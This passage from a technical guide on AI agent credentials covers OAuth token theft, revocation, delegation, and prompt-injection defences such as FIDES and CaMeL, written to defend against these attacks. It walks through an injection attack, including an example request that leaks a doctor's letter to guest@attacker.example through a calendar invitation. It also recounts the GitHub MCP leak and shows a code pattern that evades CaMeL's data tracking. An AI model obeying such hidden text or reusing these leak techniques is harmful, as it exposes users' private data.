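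One of the victims, the internet company Cloudflare (2025), published a timeline. The attackers first logged in to its Salesforce account on 12 August and spent several days studying the data and the API's limits. On 17 August they copied the text of its support tickets in three minutes and 22 seconds, then deleted the export job to hide what they had done. Cloudflare learned of the theft six days later. It found 104 Cloudflare API tokens in the stolen text, replaced them all and saw no sign of misuse.

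Salesloft and Salesforce revoked Drift's access and refresh tokens on 20 August. At first, Salesloft believed the theft affected only customers who had connected Drift to Salesforce. On 28 August, Larsen and colleagues confirmed that the attackers had also stolen tokens for Drift Email and used them on 9 August to read a very small number of Google Workspace accounts. Google then revoked those tokens.

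For connections that used OAuth, Salesloft could replace the keys that identified Drift to other services, which made the stolen tokens useless. Customers who had given Drift API keys had to revoke each one themselves at the service that issued it.

Accepting each customer's Drift token only from approved network addresses could have stopped many of these calls. According to Clari/Salesloft, genuine Drift traffic came only from a known list of addresses. The attackers used rented servers and Tor, a network that hides a user's address.

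### How much a thief can do with a stolen token

A simple calculation gives an upper limit on the number of calls a thief can make:

```
maximum calls = calls allowed per minute × minutes until the token stops working
```

Suppose someone steals a token for Alice's mailbox just after Google issues it. She has 40,000 messages, each call returns one message, and the service allows 100 calls a minute. In the last row, someone revokes the token after 12 days, the time between the first known use of the Drift tokens and their revocation.

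| Token lifetime | Maximum calls | Share of Alice's mail the thief could copy |
|---|---|---|
| Ten minutes | 1,000 | 2.5% |
| One hour | 6,000 | 15% |
| No expiry | 1,728,000 | All of it, in less than seven hours |

These figures ignore the few calls needed to list the messages. A lower rate limit helps as much as a shorter lifetime. At ten calls a minute, a thief with the one-hour token could copy only 600 messages.

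However, the number of calls doesn't measure the damage. If one call could return 500 messages, the thief could copy the whole mailbox in 80 calls, which would take less than a minute. Cloudflare's attackers used a bulk export, so even a ten-minute token would have lasted long enough for the final theft. Deleting the PocketOS database took a single call. Short lifetimes work best against slow copying and against thieves who need time to look around, as Cloudflare's attackers did, so bulk exports and deletions need their own limits.

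### Refresh tokens and rotation

A ten-minute access token protects Alice much less if the thief also has the refresh token. If the refresh token never expires, he can keep renewing his access, and the last row of the table applies again.

Refresh-token rotation makes this kind of theft easier to detect. Each time the agent's program uses a refresh token, the authorization server issues a new one and cancels the old one. Suppose Dayplan, the scheduling agent, holds refresh token R1 and a thief copies it:

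1. The thief uses R1 first and receives a new access token and R2.
2. Later, Dayplan tries to use R1.
3. The authorization server sees that someone has already used R1. It can't tell which of the two is the thief, so it cancels R2 as well.
4. Dayplan has to ask Alice to log in again, and the thief can't obtain any more tokens.

If Dayplan uses R1 first, the thief's attempt triggers the same response. When a client can't prove its identity with a secret or key of its own, Lodderstedt and colleagues require its refresh tokens to be either rotated or tied to a key. Oracle describes a product that revokes all the refresh tokens it has issued when it detects reuse.

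Rotation detects the theft only when the thief and Alice's agent both use the same token. If her agent makes no calls during a two-week holiday, the thief can keep getting new tokens throughout. An access token he already has may also work until it expires.

False alarms are another problem. If the network drops the server's answer, Dayplan never receives R2 and may try R1 again, which looks like theft. Two copies of an agent that share a refresh token can also set off a false alarm, unless a broker does all the renewals, one at a time.

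### Tokens tied to a key

A proof-of-possession token, unlike a bearer token, works only with a private key, which the client never sends. *OAuth 2.0 Demonstrating Proof of Possession (DPoP)* (Fett, Campbell and colleagues, 2023) defines one way to do this. Dayplan creates a key pair and signs its token request with the private key. The authorization server then ties the new token to the matching public key.

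For every call, Dayplan also signs a new proof. The main part of one might look like this:

```
{
  "jti": "c81e-72aa",
  "htm": "POST",
  "htu": "https://mcp.cal.example/mcp",
  "iat": 1791792600,
  "ath": "HASH-OF-THE-ACCESS-TOKEN"
}
```

The "jti" is a unique number, "htm" and "htu" are the HTTP method and address of the call, and "iat" is the time Dayplan made the proof. The last field ties the proof to one access token. The service checks the signature, compares these values with the call it received, and checks that the public key is the one tied to the token. A thief who finds the token in a log file can't make a valid proof for a new call.

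The proof doesn't cover the body of the request. With MCP, a harmless tool call and a dangerous one can both be POST requests to the same address, so the proof doesn't show which tool Dayplan meant to call. Fett and colleagues rely on the encrypted connection to protect the message itself.

Mutual TLS is an alternative. In TLS, the encryption behind HTTPS, normally only the server presents a certificate to prove its identity. In mutual TLS, the client presents one too, and the authorization server can tie the token to it. This suits a company's own servers, but Fett and colleagues explain that it works poorly for programs that run inside a browser, which is one reason they designed DPoP.

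Neither method helps if the attacker controls the agent's program. Fett and colleagues give the example of hostile code in a web page. Even if the browser prevents the code from copying the private key, the code can have the browser sign proofs with it. It could also prepare proofs dated in the future and send them to the attacker for later use. A service can prevent that by requiring each proof to contain a recent random value from the service, but the hostile code can still make calls while it is running.

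An attacker may not need to run code. If hostile text causes the model to request a call, Dayplan's own software will sign the proof as usual, and the signature will correctly show that the call came from Dayplan.

At Drift, the benefit would have depended on where Salesloft kept the private keys. If Salesloft had stored them next to the tokens, the attackers could have copied both. If it had kept them in hardware that signs messages but never releases a key, the attackers would have needed continued access to Drift's systems to make new proofs.

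### Passing authority to another agent

Agents can also pass work on to other agents. Suppose Dayplan asks a second agent, Roomfinder, to check when Alice is free and find a meeting room. If Dayplan hands over its own token, Roomfinder can do everything Dayplan can, and the calendar service can't distinguish between their requests.

Jones, Nadalin and colleagues, in *OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange*, define a safer way. Dayplan sends the authorization server a subject token, which shows that it acts for Alice, and an actor token, which identifies Roomfinder. It also asks for a narrower scope. If the server agrees, it issues a new token for Roomfinder:

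```
{
  "iss": "https://auth.cal.example",
  "sub": "user-4821",
  "aud": "https://mcp.cal.example",
  "exp": 1791793200,
  "scope": "events:read",
  "act": {
    "sub": "https://roomfinder.example",
    "act": {"sub": "https://dayplan.example"}
  }
}
```

The "sub" (subject) field still identifies Alice. The outer "act" field identifies the agent that is acting now, and the inner one identifies the agent that passed on the work. If Roomfinder behaves badly, the calendar service can block it without blocking Dayplan.

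This is delegation, in which the token identifies both the user and the agent. The same standard allows impersonation, in which the token identifies only the user. Token Protocol Explorer, a demonstration site, shows that such a token has no "act" field and looks just like one the user obtained directly. Impersonation can be convenient with older services that recognise only users, but it is a poor choice for agents because the token does not show that an agent made the call.

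A chain of names is only as reliable as the authorization servers that write it. Under the standard, a service can base its decision on the current actor, but earlier actors are listed for information only. *Cryptographically Verifiable Actor Chains for OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange* (Prasad, Krishnan and colleagues, 2026) points out that the standard has no common rules for preserving or checking the chain over several exchanges. The draft proposes six ways to do so, which differ in how much of the chain each recipient can see.

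### Macaroons: narrowing a token without asking the issuer

With token exchange, Dayplan has to contact the authorization server for every narrower token. A macaroon is a token that its holder can narrow without contacting anyone. A macaroon uses HMAC, a function that combines a secret key with some text to produce a short code. Nobody can produce the right code without the key, or work out the key from the code.

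Suppose the calendar service gives Dayplan a macaroon, and Dayplan adds two restrictions, called caveats, before passing it to Roomfinder:

```
code0 = HMAC(service's secret key, "calendar token 9f2c")
code1 = HMAC(code0, "operation = events.list")
code2 = HMAC(code1, "time < 2026-10-12T08:20Z")
```

Dayplan has code0, so it can calculate the other two codes itself. It gives Roomfinder the token's name, the two caveats and code2, but not the other two codes. When Roomfinder makes a call, the service starts from its secret key, repeats all three calculations and compares the result with code2. It then checks that the call meets both caveats.

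Roomfinder can add a third caveat by using code2 as the key, but it can't remove the time limit, because doing so would require code1. An agent can therefore give each helper narrower authority than its own, even when the authorization server is offline. A thief who copies the macaroon can still use it within its caveats.

Prakash (2026), in *AIP*, lists two weaknesses of macaroons. First, every service that checks a macaroon needs the secret key, so it could also forge new ones. This is acceptable inside one company but not between companies that don't trust each other. Second, Prakash says caveats are too simple for time limits and budgets. That seems overstated for time limits, since the service decides what a caveat means and can compare a time with its clock. A shared budget is harder because someone has to keep track of spending.

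Biscuit, a newer token format, avoids the first weakness by using public keys, so a service can check a token without being able to create one.

### Whether OAuth is enough across organisations

In the example above, Dayplan and Roomfinder use the same authorization server. It gets harder when Alice's employer, her agent's maker and the services they use all have their own. Prakash argues that OAuth can't handle this well, for three reasons:

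- Each organisation needs its own authorization server, and the organisations have to arrange in advance to accept each other's tokens.
- Token exchange produces a new token with no record of who passed the authority on.
- The holder of a token can't narrow it without contacting the server.

The second objection is overstated, because the nested "act" field can record earlier actors, although there are no common rules for checking them. The third objection is correct for ordinary OAuth tokens, but it matters only when the extra request is slow or the server is unavailable.

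Prakash proposes the Agent Identity Protocol (AIP) as an alternative. An AIP token starts with a signed block that records who gave the authority, the permissions, a budget, an expiry time and how many times agents may pass it on. Each agent that passes it on adds a signed block, which can only narrow the permissions. The last agent can add a record of the result. In Prakash's tests, AIP rejected all 600 attempted attacks. In a trial with several agents, it added 2.35 milliseconds, less than 0.1% of the total time. These are the designer's own tests, so they are better evidence that AIP adds little delay than that it can stop a determined attacker.

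AIP also still requires trust between organisations. A signature can prove that dayplan.example approved a call, but the calendar service still has to confirm that Alice allowed Dayplan to act for her. Prakash objects to another identity system on much the same grounds, because the service needs some outside reason to trust an identity. He also calls OAuth the better choice within a single organisation and describes AIP as a complement to MCP's use of OAuth, which narrows the disagreement.

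Prakash may also overstate the problem. He cites a 2025 scan in which none of about 2,000 MCP servers required authentication, but most of the live servers in Zhou and colleagues' larger study required it.

*AI Identity* (Otsuka, Toyoda and Leung, 2026) rates OAuth as "partial" because it works well when a user delegates to one agent but not when that agent delegates to others. The paper also cites figures suggesting that many organisations have a more basic problem, with only 21.9% treating agents as having their own identities and 45.6% running them on shared API keys. For a company that uses shared keys, giving each agent its own credential would help more than a new protocol for delegation chains.

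Ibrahim and Li (2026), in *Overlaying Governance*, object that a token's contents stay the same after the server issues it, even if the situation changes. They propose a live record of who has delegated what to whom, that the system checks on each request. An employee could then let an agent read her mail only while it is inside the company's network. But the record has to be available whenever the agent acts.

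Others want to extend OAuth instead of replacing it. In *Authenticated Delegation and Authorized AI Agents* (2025), South and colleagues propose adding a delegation token that links an agent to the user it acts for. Ibrahim and Li note that companies can reuse their existing login systems this way. *OAuth Actor Profile for Delegation* (McGuinness, 2026) proposes common rules for the fields in such tokens, so that every service can tell the user, the registered program and the acting agent apart.

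Enterprise-managed authorization, an optional extension to MCP, lets an employer's administrator decide in advance which agents may connect to which services. An employee then logs in once through the employer's identity provider, the system that manages staff logins. The identity provider gives the agent a signed statement, and the service's authorization server exchanges this for an access token without showing the employee another consent page. The employer can block an agent for all its staff in one place. But each service has to agree beforehand to trust the employer's identity provider, and Prakash considers this kind of arrangement a limitation of OAuth.

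Most IETF work on agents was still in draft in mid-2026. Authors can change or abandon a draft, and it expires after six months unless they renew it. Prakash found that the authorization section of AIMS, a prominent draft, contained only "TODO Security", and Otsuka and colleagues also found the draft's security sections unfinished. A developer who needs delegation now can use token exchange within one organisation, but should keep the delegation chain short and check how each service treats the "act" field.

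### Revoking access

Alice can usually withdraw an agent's access on a settings page at the service. Cloudflare's page, for example, shows which programs have access, to which accounts and with which scopes, according to Hutchings and colleagues. The agent's maker can often cancel its own tokens as well, and an employer's administrator may be able to cancel those of all its staff. How quickly this works depends on the credential:

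| Credential | When it stops working after someone revokes it |
|---|---|
| Signed access token | When it expires, unless the service keeps a list of cancelled tokens |
| Access token that the service looks up | At the next lookup |
| Refresh token | At the next renewal, though existing access tokens may keep working |
| API key | Usually at the next call |

A service that looks up tokens may save each answer to avoid repeating the request. If it saves answers for 60 seconds, a revoked token can keep working for up to a minute. An agent making 100 calls a minute could make up to 100 more calls in that time, compared with 6,000 using a signed token that still has an hour left.

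In Jones and colleagues' standard, cancelling a token doesn't automatically cancel the delegated tokens that a client obtained in exchange for it, so these are easy to miss. If Alice disconnects Dayplan, Roomfinder's token may still work. Giving every delegated token a short lifetime limits how long this access can last.

Some services revoke leaked keys automatically. Hutchings and colleagues explain how this works at Cloudflare:

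1. New Cloudflare tokens begin with a recognisable prefix and end with a checksum, a few characters calculated from the rest of the token.
2. GitHub scans every new change to a repository for text in this format and uses the checksum to rule out lookalikes.
3. If a token appears in a public repository, GitHub notifies Cloudflare.
4. Cloudflare revokes the token and emails its owner.

If the repository is private, GitHub warns the owner, but Cloudflare doesn't revoke the token automatically. Older tokens lack the new format, so scanners may miss them until the owner replaces them. Hutchings and colleagues give no figures for how long the process takes, and an attacker scanning the same repositories may find the token first. Automatic revocation also can't help with a token that someone leaks in a private chat or steals from a server, as happened at Drift.

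### Credentials an agent acquires while working

An agent may also create new credentials, for example by registering an account, renting a server or generating an API key. Revoking the agent's original token doesn't necessarily remove any of these. Attackers can exploit this too. Salesloft's attackers added a guest user to its GitHub account, and that user's access could outlast the credential used to create it.

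Zhu and Wang describe an agent that has permission to spend $20 on a server that can only read data. The price is right, the payment goes through and the provider delivers a server, but it comes with an administrator's credential and can change things outside the task. The ordinary checks all succeed because they cover the purchase and not the permissions of what the agent receives. A price limit also doesn't stop an agent from creating four free accounts when its task allows one, and a refund may return the money without cancelling the credential.

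In one proposal, a broker holds each new resource in quarantine, queries the provider to find out what the resource can actually do, and compares the answer with the limits of the task. The agent receives a handle only after this comparison, and the broker checks every later use. If the broker can't determine what the resource permits, the agent can't use it.

In tests on five kinds of resource, the system accepted all 20 legitimate sequences of actions and rejected all 40 unsafe ones. In a separate test with Docker, which runs programs in isolated containers, none of the 16 unsafe cases led to an unauthorised start. Zhu and Wang chose these cases themselves, and the results depend on the provider reporting a resource's permissions correctly. The design also requires the provider to hand new credentials to the broker, which isn't possible if a website displays a new key on a page the agent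 is reading.

A developer can apply part of this idea without building the whole system. If the task doesn't require new accounts or keys, the agent's credential should not let it create them. If the task does require them, the broker can record each one with its owner and an expiry date, then delete the account or key when the task ends. If the agent's credential is stolen, the record shows which other credentials to revoke, though the developer should also search the service for accounts and keys missing from it.

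## Hostile text that misuses permitted actions

A credential broker keeps an attacker from copying Alice's token, but if he can get her agent to read his text, the agent may use the token for him.

Suppose an attacker emails Alice an invitation to a budget review. Below the visible details he adds instructions for the agent, in white letters on a white background. Alice then asks her agent to add her new invitations to her calendar:

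1. The agent lists her new messages and opens the invitation, including the hidden text.
2. The model treats the hidden text as part of its task. It looks through her mailbox and opens a letter from her doctor.
3. It creates the event, with the letter in the description and the attacker as a guest.
4. The event appears on the attacker's own calendar, where he can read the letter.

The request in step 3 would look like this:

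```
POST /calendar/v3/calendars/primary/events
Authorization: Bearer ACCESS-TOKEN

{
  "summary": "Budget review",
  "start": {"dateTime": "2026-10-15T10:00:00+02:00"},
  "end":   {"dateTime": "2026-10-15T11:00:00+02:00"},
  "description": "TEXT OF THE DOCTOR'S LETTER",
  "attendees": [{"email": "guest@attacker.example"}]
}
```

The attack needs only gmail.readonly and calendar.events.owned, the two narrow scopes that Alice's task requires. The request passes Google's checks because the token is valid, the scope is sufficient and Alice may write to her own calendar. Nothing in the request looks wrong, since many ordinary events have notes and outside guests.

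### The confused deputy

A confused deputy is a program tricked into using its legitimate authority for someone who lacks that authority. The attacker isn't allowed to read Alice's mail, but her agent is, and Google checks only the agent's permissions.

Short-lived tokens and tokens tied to a key don't help here, because the call comes from the right program. Other programs can become confused deputies too, such as an MCP server that forwards a token meant for another service. Agents are especially prone to this problem because a language model receives Alice's request and the attacker's email as text in the same conversation.

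### The GitHub MCP case

Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) demonstrated such a leak with GitHub's official MCP server, which connects agents to GitHub accounts. The researchers at this security company set up an account with a public repository and several private ones:

1. They filed an issue containing hostile instructions in the public repository, as anyone on GitHub could have done.
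2. The user asked Claude Desktop, running Claude 4 Opus, to look at that repository's open issues.
3. The agent read the issue and then used the same connection to read the private repositories.
4. It published what it had found in a pull request, a proposed change to a project, on the public repository.

Anyone could then read the names of the user's private projects, their salary and a plan to move to South America. The repositories were demonstrations, so the attack had no real victim.

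The GitHub MCP server had no bug. heise online's *Attack via GitHub MCP server* explains that the server could reach the private data because it worked through the user's account. DevClass' *Researchers warn of prompt injection vulnerability in GitHub MCP* reports that Claude Desktop asks users to confirm each tool call by default, but that the researchers suspect many choose "always allow".

A token limited to the public repository would have prevented the leak, because the agent would have had no private data to publish. GitHub had made its fine-grained tokens, which can be limited this way, generally available two months earlier. A token that could read issues but not write would also have prevented the leak, because the agent could not have opened the pull request.

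Invariant Labs recommends giving agents access only to the repositories they need, but considers ordinary token permissions too rigid. It suggests adding a rule that limits an agent to one repository per session, enforced by software it sells. The rule would have blocked the attack even with a broad token. However, it would also block legitimate work that spans two repositories, and it covers only the operations it lists.

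Newer models are much harder to mislead in tests. But a user can still give an agent a token that covers both public and private repositories, and Invariant Labs argues that GitHub can't solve the problem just by changing its server.

### Dangerous combinations of scopes

In *GitHub MCP Exploited*, Willison calls the underlying problem the "lethal trifecta", in which an agent has access to private data, reads text that may contain malicious instructions, and can send information out. A developer can avoid this kind of leak by never giving an agent all three at once.

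The rule applies to the whole grant, because two scopes that are fairly safe alone can complete the combination:

| Grant | Private data | Text from strangers | Way to send data out |
|---|---|---|---|
| gmail.readonly | Mail | Yes | No |
| gmail.send | No | No | Yes |
| gmail.readonly and gmail.send | Mail | Yes | Yes |
| calendar.events.owned | Events | Yes, in other people's invitations | Yes, by adding guests |
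| gmail.readonly and calendar.events.owned | Mail and events | Yes | Yes |

If an agent has both gmail.readonly and gmail.send, a stranger's email can cause it to leak the whole mailbox. With only gmail.readonly, the agent can read the hostile email but can't use Gmail to send anything out, and with only gmail.send, it has no mail to leak. The calendar scope alone creates the same risk for calendar data, because it lets the agent read strangers' invitations, read private events and send invitations to others. Adding gmail.readonly exposes the mail as well.

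Tools that look for the smallest grant don't catch scopes that are harmless alone but dangerous together. MiniScope adds up the methods that each scope permits, so two such scopes get a good score if they permit few methods. Consent pages don't help much either when the scopes belong to different companies. If an agent reads mail at Google and posts messages on Slack, each company asks the user only about its own scopes.

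The developer has to check every tool the agent can use, including those that need no token, because even a tool that opens web pages can leak data through the addresses it requests.

The agent needs Alice's mail for its task, and other people write the invitations it reads, so its ability to send data out is the easiest part to remove. A rule against adding guests, like the one in the Progent example, would block the request above, but Alice would then have to add guests herself.

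A rule can also depend on what the agent has already done. For example, it could allow guests at the start of a session and forbid them once the agent has opened an email. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents*, a survey by Zhou and Zhang (2026), describes a system called Bounded Agents that records the agent's actions and rejects forbidden combinations. Its guarantee assumes that the restrictions are adequate and that the system decides on one action at a time. If it decided on two at once, it could approve both before either appeared in the history.

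### How often attacks succeed

How often a model follows hostile text depends on the setting, the number of attempts, any extra safeguards around the model, and whether the attacker adapts the text after seeing what fails. Anthropic tests its browser agent with an adaptive attacker that tries and combines many techniques known to work.

The table gives results for three Claude models and one OpenAI model from 2026. The figures for Opus 4.6 and 4.8 come from two VentureBeat reports on Anthropic's system cards, documents that describe a model's tests. The others come from *Anthropic's Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (Schneier, 2026), which quotes results on a test by the security company Gray Swan.

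| Model | Setting | Attempts | Extra safeguards | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Coding | 200 | No | 0% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Graphical interface | 1 | No | 17.8% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Graphical interface | 200 | No | 78.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Graphical interface | 200 | Yes | 57.1% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | Coding, adaptive attacker | 1 | No | 7.03% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | Coding, adaptive attacker | 1 | Yes | 2.09% |
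| Claude Opus 5 | Gray Swan's general test | 15 | – | 2.0% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | Gray Swan's general test | 1 | – | 3.1% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | Gray Swan's general test | 15 | – | 20.0% |

VentureBeat gives an attack success rate without safeguards of about 31% for Opus 4.8 in a browser. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that none of the attacks on the next model, Opus 5, succeeded in 129 test scenarios as a browser agent. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Opus 5.5, published in September, reports results similar to or better than Opus 5's on every prompt injection test it includes. Anthropic's *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (2026) announced two newer models on 9 November.

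Repeated attempts make an attack much more likely to succeed. On GPT-5.6 Sol, 20.0% of attacks succeeded within 15 attempts. If each attempt had an independent 3.1% chance, the figure would be about 38%, which suggests that the successes cluster in certain test cases while every attempt fails in others. An attacker can also send the same email to thousands of people, so even a low success rate may be enough.

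In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, independent researchers Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) found that attack success varied widely between models. They tested tool-calling agents on 949 cases per model, using prepared, non-adaptive attacks. Without extra defences, the attacks succeeded in 36.1% of cases against GPT-4.1, 24.6% against Gemini 2.5 Pro, 2.1% against Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite, 1.5% against Claude Fable 5 and 0.0% against GPT-5.5.

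A low rate in this test doesn't always mean a model is secure. Flash Lite completed only 27.8% of the ordinary tasks, so it may have been too weak to carry out many of the attacks. Fable 5 refused 52 of the 97 ordinary tasks, even though they contained no attack. GPT-5.5 had a perfect score in this test, but Schneier gives it a rate of 20.8% within 15 attempts in Gray Swan's test.

None of these tests gave a browser agent and an API agent the same tasks and attacks, so their figures can't be compared directly. The Opus 4.8 results come closest because they involve the same class of attack, but writing code and using websites are different tasks. A successful attack in a logged-in browser can also do more harm, because the session has broader rights than a scoped token.

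### Splitting the task between two agents

A developer can also break up the dangerous combination by dividing the work. One agent for Alice could hold a token for gmail.readonly and nothing else. It reads each email and fills in a form:

```
{
  "title": "Budget review",
  "start": "2026-10-15T10:00:00+02:00",
  "end":   "2026-10-15T11:00:00+02:00"
}
```

Ordinary software checks that the times are valid and the title is short, then passes the form to a second agent, which has the calendar token but never sees an email. The hidden text can't add guests or a description because the form has no fields for them. For a job this simple, a few lines of ordinary code can make the API call instead of the second agent.

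The reading agent may still follow the hidden text. It could enter the wrong time, invent a meeting or put a private detail in the title, and even a short title can hold a password. But without guests, only people who can already see Alice's calendar will see the title.

The main drawback is reduced flexibility. The form omits the agenda and the video call link unless the developer adds fields for them, and each free-text field gives an attacker more space for hostile instructions. Some requests also need both kinds of access at once. If a colleague writes "let's meet right after the budget review", the reading agent can't look up when the review ends, and the writing agent never sees the message.

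### FIDES: labels on data

FIDES and CaMeL are designed to keep more of this flexibility. Both use one model that plans and calls tools, and a second, quarantined model that reads untrusted text but has no tools. Software around the models tracks where each piece of data came from and restricts where it may go.

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, describe FIDES, which comes from Microsoft. It attaches two labels to data. An integrity label marks the data as trusted or untrusted, and a confidentiality label lists the people who may read it. When the agent combines two pieces of data, the result is untrusted if either piece was, and only people who may read both pieces may read the result:

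```
Doctor's letter:   {Alice, doctor}
Invitation:        {Alice, attacker}
Both together:     {Alice, doctor} ∩ {Alice, attacker} = {Alice}
```

FIDES checks these labels before every tool call. One rule permits a consequential action, such as creating an event, only if trusted information led to the call. Another permits sending data only to people who are allowed to read it. The second rule would stop the agent from putting the doctor's letter into an event that the attacker can see.

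One of Costa and colleagues' examples is almost exactly Alice's task. The agent has to read three emails, check whether any of them asks for a meeting and create the event:

1. The planning model requests the emails. FIDES stores their contents in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name.
2. The planning model has the quarantined model check the variable for a meeting request. The quarantined model can answer only yes or no.
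3. The planning model looks at the answer. If it is yes, it has the quarantined model extract the details in a fixed format, which FIDES stores in another variable.
4. The planning model creates the event from that variable, without ever seeing the text of an email.

The answer in step 2 is still untrusted, because a hostile email could change it. Under the strict version of the first rule, the agent could no longer create an event after seeing that answer. FIDES can make an exception for a yes-or-no answer, since one word is unlikely to carry an attacker's instructions.

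Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on the benchmark *AgentDojo* (2024), which has 97 ordinary tasks and 70 tools. They counted 152 successful attacks with GPT-4o and no defence, and none with FIDES's rules switched on. The benchmark's automatic scoring recorded three successful attacks with the rules on, which they judged to be harmless or misclassified.

The price was a large drop in completed tasks. These figures are for runs without attacks:

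| Setting | Ordinary agent, no rules | Ordinary agent with the rules | FIDES with the rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office work | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |
| Average | 84.3% | 41.9% | 50.0% |

Costa and colleagues emphasise that FIDES completed 8 percentage points more tasks than an ordinary agent under the same rules, and 16 points more with OpenAI's o1 model. But FIDES with GPT-4o completed 34 points fewer than the unprotected agent. Some of that loss was intentional, because several tasks require the agent to follow instructions from an untrusted file.

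The labels in the experiment were also easier to choose than they would be in practice. The researchers marked a field as untrusted if at least one attack in the benchmark used it. A developer doesn't know where attacks will appear, and an attacker can exploit any field wrongly marked as trusted. The researchers also left out the restricted yes-or-no answers that Alice's task would use, because most tasks in the benchmark didn't need them.

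### CaMeL: planning before reading

CaMeL has the planning model write the whole procedure as a program before the agent reads any outside text. For Alice, a simplified version might look like this:

```
for message in list_messages():
    event = quarantined_model("Extract the invitation, if any", message)
    if event.found:
        create_event(event.title, event.start, event.end)
```

The program never adds guests or a description, so the hidden text can't make it do so. The text can still affect which branch runs, for example by causing the quarantined model to misclassify an advertisement as an invitation. The planning model needs the format of every tool's output in advance to write such a program, so Peters-Gill and colleagues added these formats to the tool descriptions. This is much easier when a service has complete API documentation.

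CaMeL also records the origin of each value and checks it against policies when the program calls a tool. According to *CaMeLoT* (2026), a follow-up to CaMeL, the developer writes these policies as Python functions that inspect a call and return "allow" or "deny" with a reason.

In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) reran CaMeL on AgentDojo's banking tasks with two newer models, GPT-5.2 and MiMo-v2.5. With CaMeL's policies off, only 5 of 622 completed attack runs succeeded, and the agents completed 66.7% and 70.8% of the ordinary tasks. With the policies on, none of the 588 completed attack runs succeeded, but each agent completed only 37.5% of the ordinary tasks.

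In about two-thirds of the combinations of task and attack, planning first was normally enough by itself to stop the attack, which needed an operation that the planned program would not contain. An exception was a task that told the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The planning model wrote a program with a branch for every tool, so whoever controlled the file could choose any of them.

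Garby and colleagues also found gaps in CaMeL's tracking. Suppose that a program may not email Alice's bank balance to anyone. This version, simplified from their example, reveals something about it anyway:

```
rich = True
low = True
if balance > 10000:
    low = False
if low:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("The balance is high")
```

If the balance is above 10,000, "low" becomes false and CaMeL marks it as secret. The program then skips the line that would change "rich", so CaMeL never marks that value, even though it now depends on the balance, and the email goes out. CaMeL's automatic retries create a second gap. Whether a policy blocks an attempt can reveal one yes-or-no fact about a secret, so an attacker who can trigger enough retries can learn the whole secret piece by piece.

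They also criticise FIDES because it is designed to ignore secrets that affect only which steps an agent takes, and because its exception for short answers makes a harmless release hard to distinguish from a leak. Their own system is mathematically proven to track data correctly. It completed about as many banking tasks as CaMeL without policies, and only 2 of 1,296 attacks on it succeeded.

### When protected agents talk to each other

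CaMeL protects a single agent, but this can fail when one agent gives work to another. In an experiment by Peters-Gill and colleagues, a user asked a coordinating agent to send a colleague a Slack message summarizing job applications. A second agent read the applications from a database that contained hostile text, and a third could send Slack messages and emails. All three agents used CaMeL, without any additional policies.

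The first two followed their programs correctly. But the coordinating agent put the summary, including the hostile text, into its written instructions to the sending agent. The sending agent treated everything in those instructions as trusted and wrote a program that also emailed the applicants' data to an outsider. The same thing could happen if Dayplan copied part of an email into a request to Roomfinder.

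Peters-Gill and colleagues solve this with separate fields for instructions and data. The software rejects any instruction that contains text from a tool's output, so the receiving agent's planning model never sees that text. Averaged over five models, attacks succeeded in 12.9% of cases without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent and 0.0% with the separate fields added. On a different benchmark, of 112 professional tasks, adding CaMeL to each agent lowered the completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points, and the separate fields lowered it by another 3.2 points. For the two strongest models, these two losses were 13.4 and 0.85 points.

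### What these defences cost and miss

The extra models also cost money. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) applied CaMeL to agents that operate a computer through its screen. On 17 tasks, the models wrote 35 times as much text, and the additional calls cost $5.40, or $11.57 with an extra check of the page's structure. *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (2026) surveyed 41 studies and found that 33 of the defences needed additional computation. Most also couldn't handle tasks whose next step depends on what the agent reads.

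Most of the results for FIDES and CaMeL come from AgentDojo or versions of it, and AgentDojo has problems. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) describes a task in which the agent has to pay a bill, but the hostile text replaces the bill's contents. No agent could complete that task under attack, so a low completion rate there doesn't necessarily mean that a defence hindered the agent.

A similar task also shows the limit of tracking where data came from. In both successful attacks on Garby and colleagues' system, a user asked the agent to read a file and follow its payment instructions. The agent did so, but an attacker had replaced the file's contents with his own payment request. Blocking every payment based on an untrusted file would stop the attack but also prevent the agent from paying real bills. PAuth would ask the user about such a payment, and she would have to notice the wrong account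 number.

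## Testing an agent's access and reading its logs

Any of the limits described so far can fail if it is set up wrongly, so whoever approves an agent should test them before the agent uses a real account.

### A test for Alice's agent

Suppose Alice's agent has the scopes gmail.readonly and calendar.events.owned. Its broker allows it to list messages, open a message, and create events without guests in her own calendar. The tester can proceed like this:

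1. Create two test accounts, one to stand in for Alice and one for a colleague, and put some messages and events in both. Some of the calls below really delete things, so they shouldn't run on anyone's real data.
2. Connect the agent to the first account in the same way that Alice would, and get a copy of its Google token and its session handle.
3. Send each call directly to Google with the token, which shows what a thief could do. Then send it through the broker with the handle, which shows what a misled agent could do. Leave the model out of both.
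4. Check the account after every call, because the status code can be misleading, as it is on Railway.
5. Save the results with the date, the scopes and the version of the agent's software.

| Call | Directly to Google | Through the broker |
|---|---|---|
| List messages | Allowed | Allowed |
| Open a message | Allowed | Allowed |
| Create an event without guests | Allowed | Allowed |
| Create an event with a guest | Allowed | Refused |
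| Delete an event | Allowed | Refused |
| Send an email | Refused (403) | Refused |
| Delete an email | Refused (403) | Refused |
| Share the calendar | Refused (403) | Refused |
| Create an event in the colleague's calendar | Refused (403 or 404) | Refused |
| List messages with an expired token or session | Refused (401) | Refused |
| List messages with another service's token | Refused (401) | – |
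| List messages after Alice revokes access | Refused (401), perhaps after a delay | Refused |

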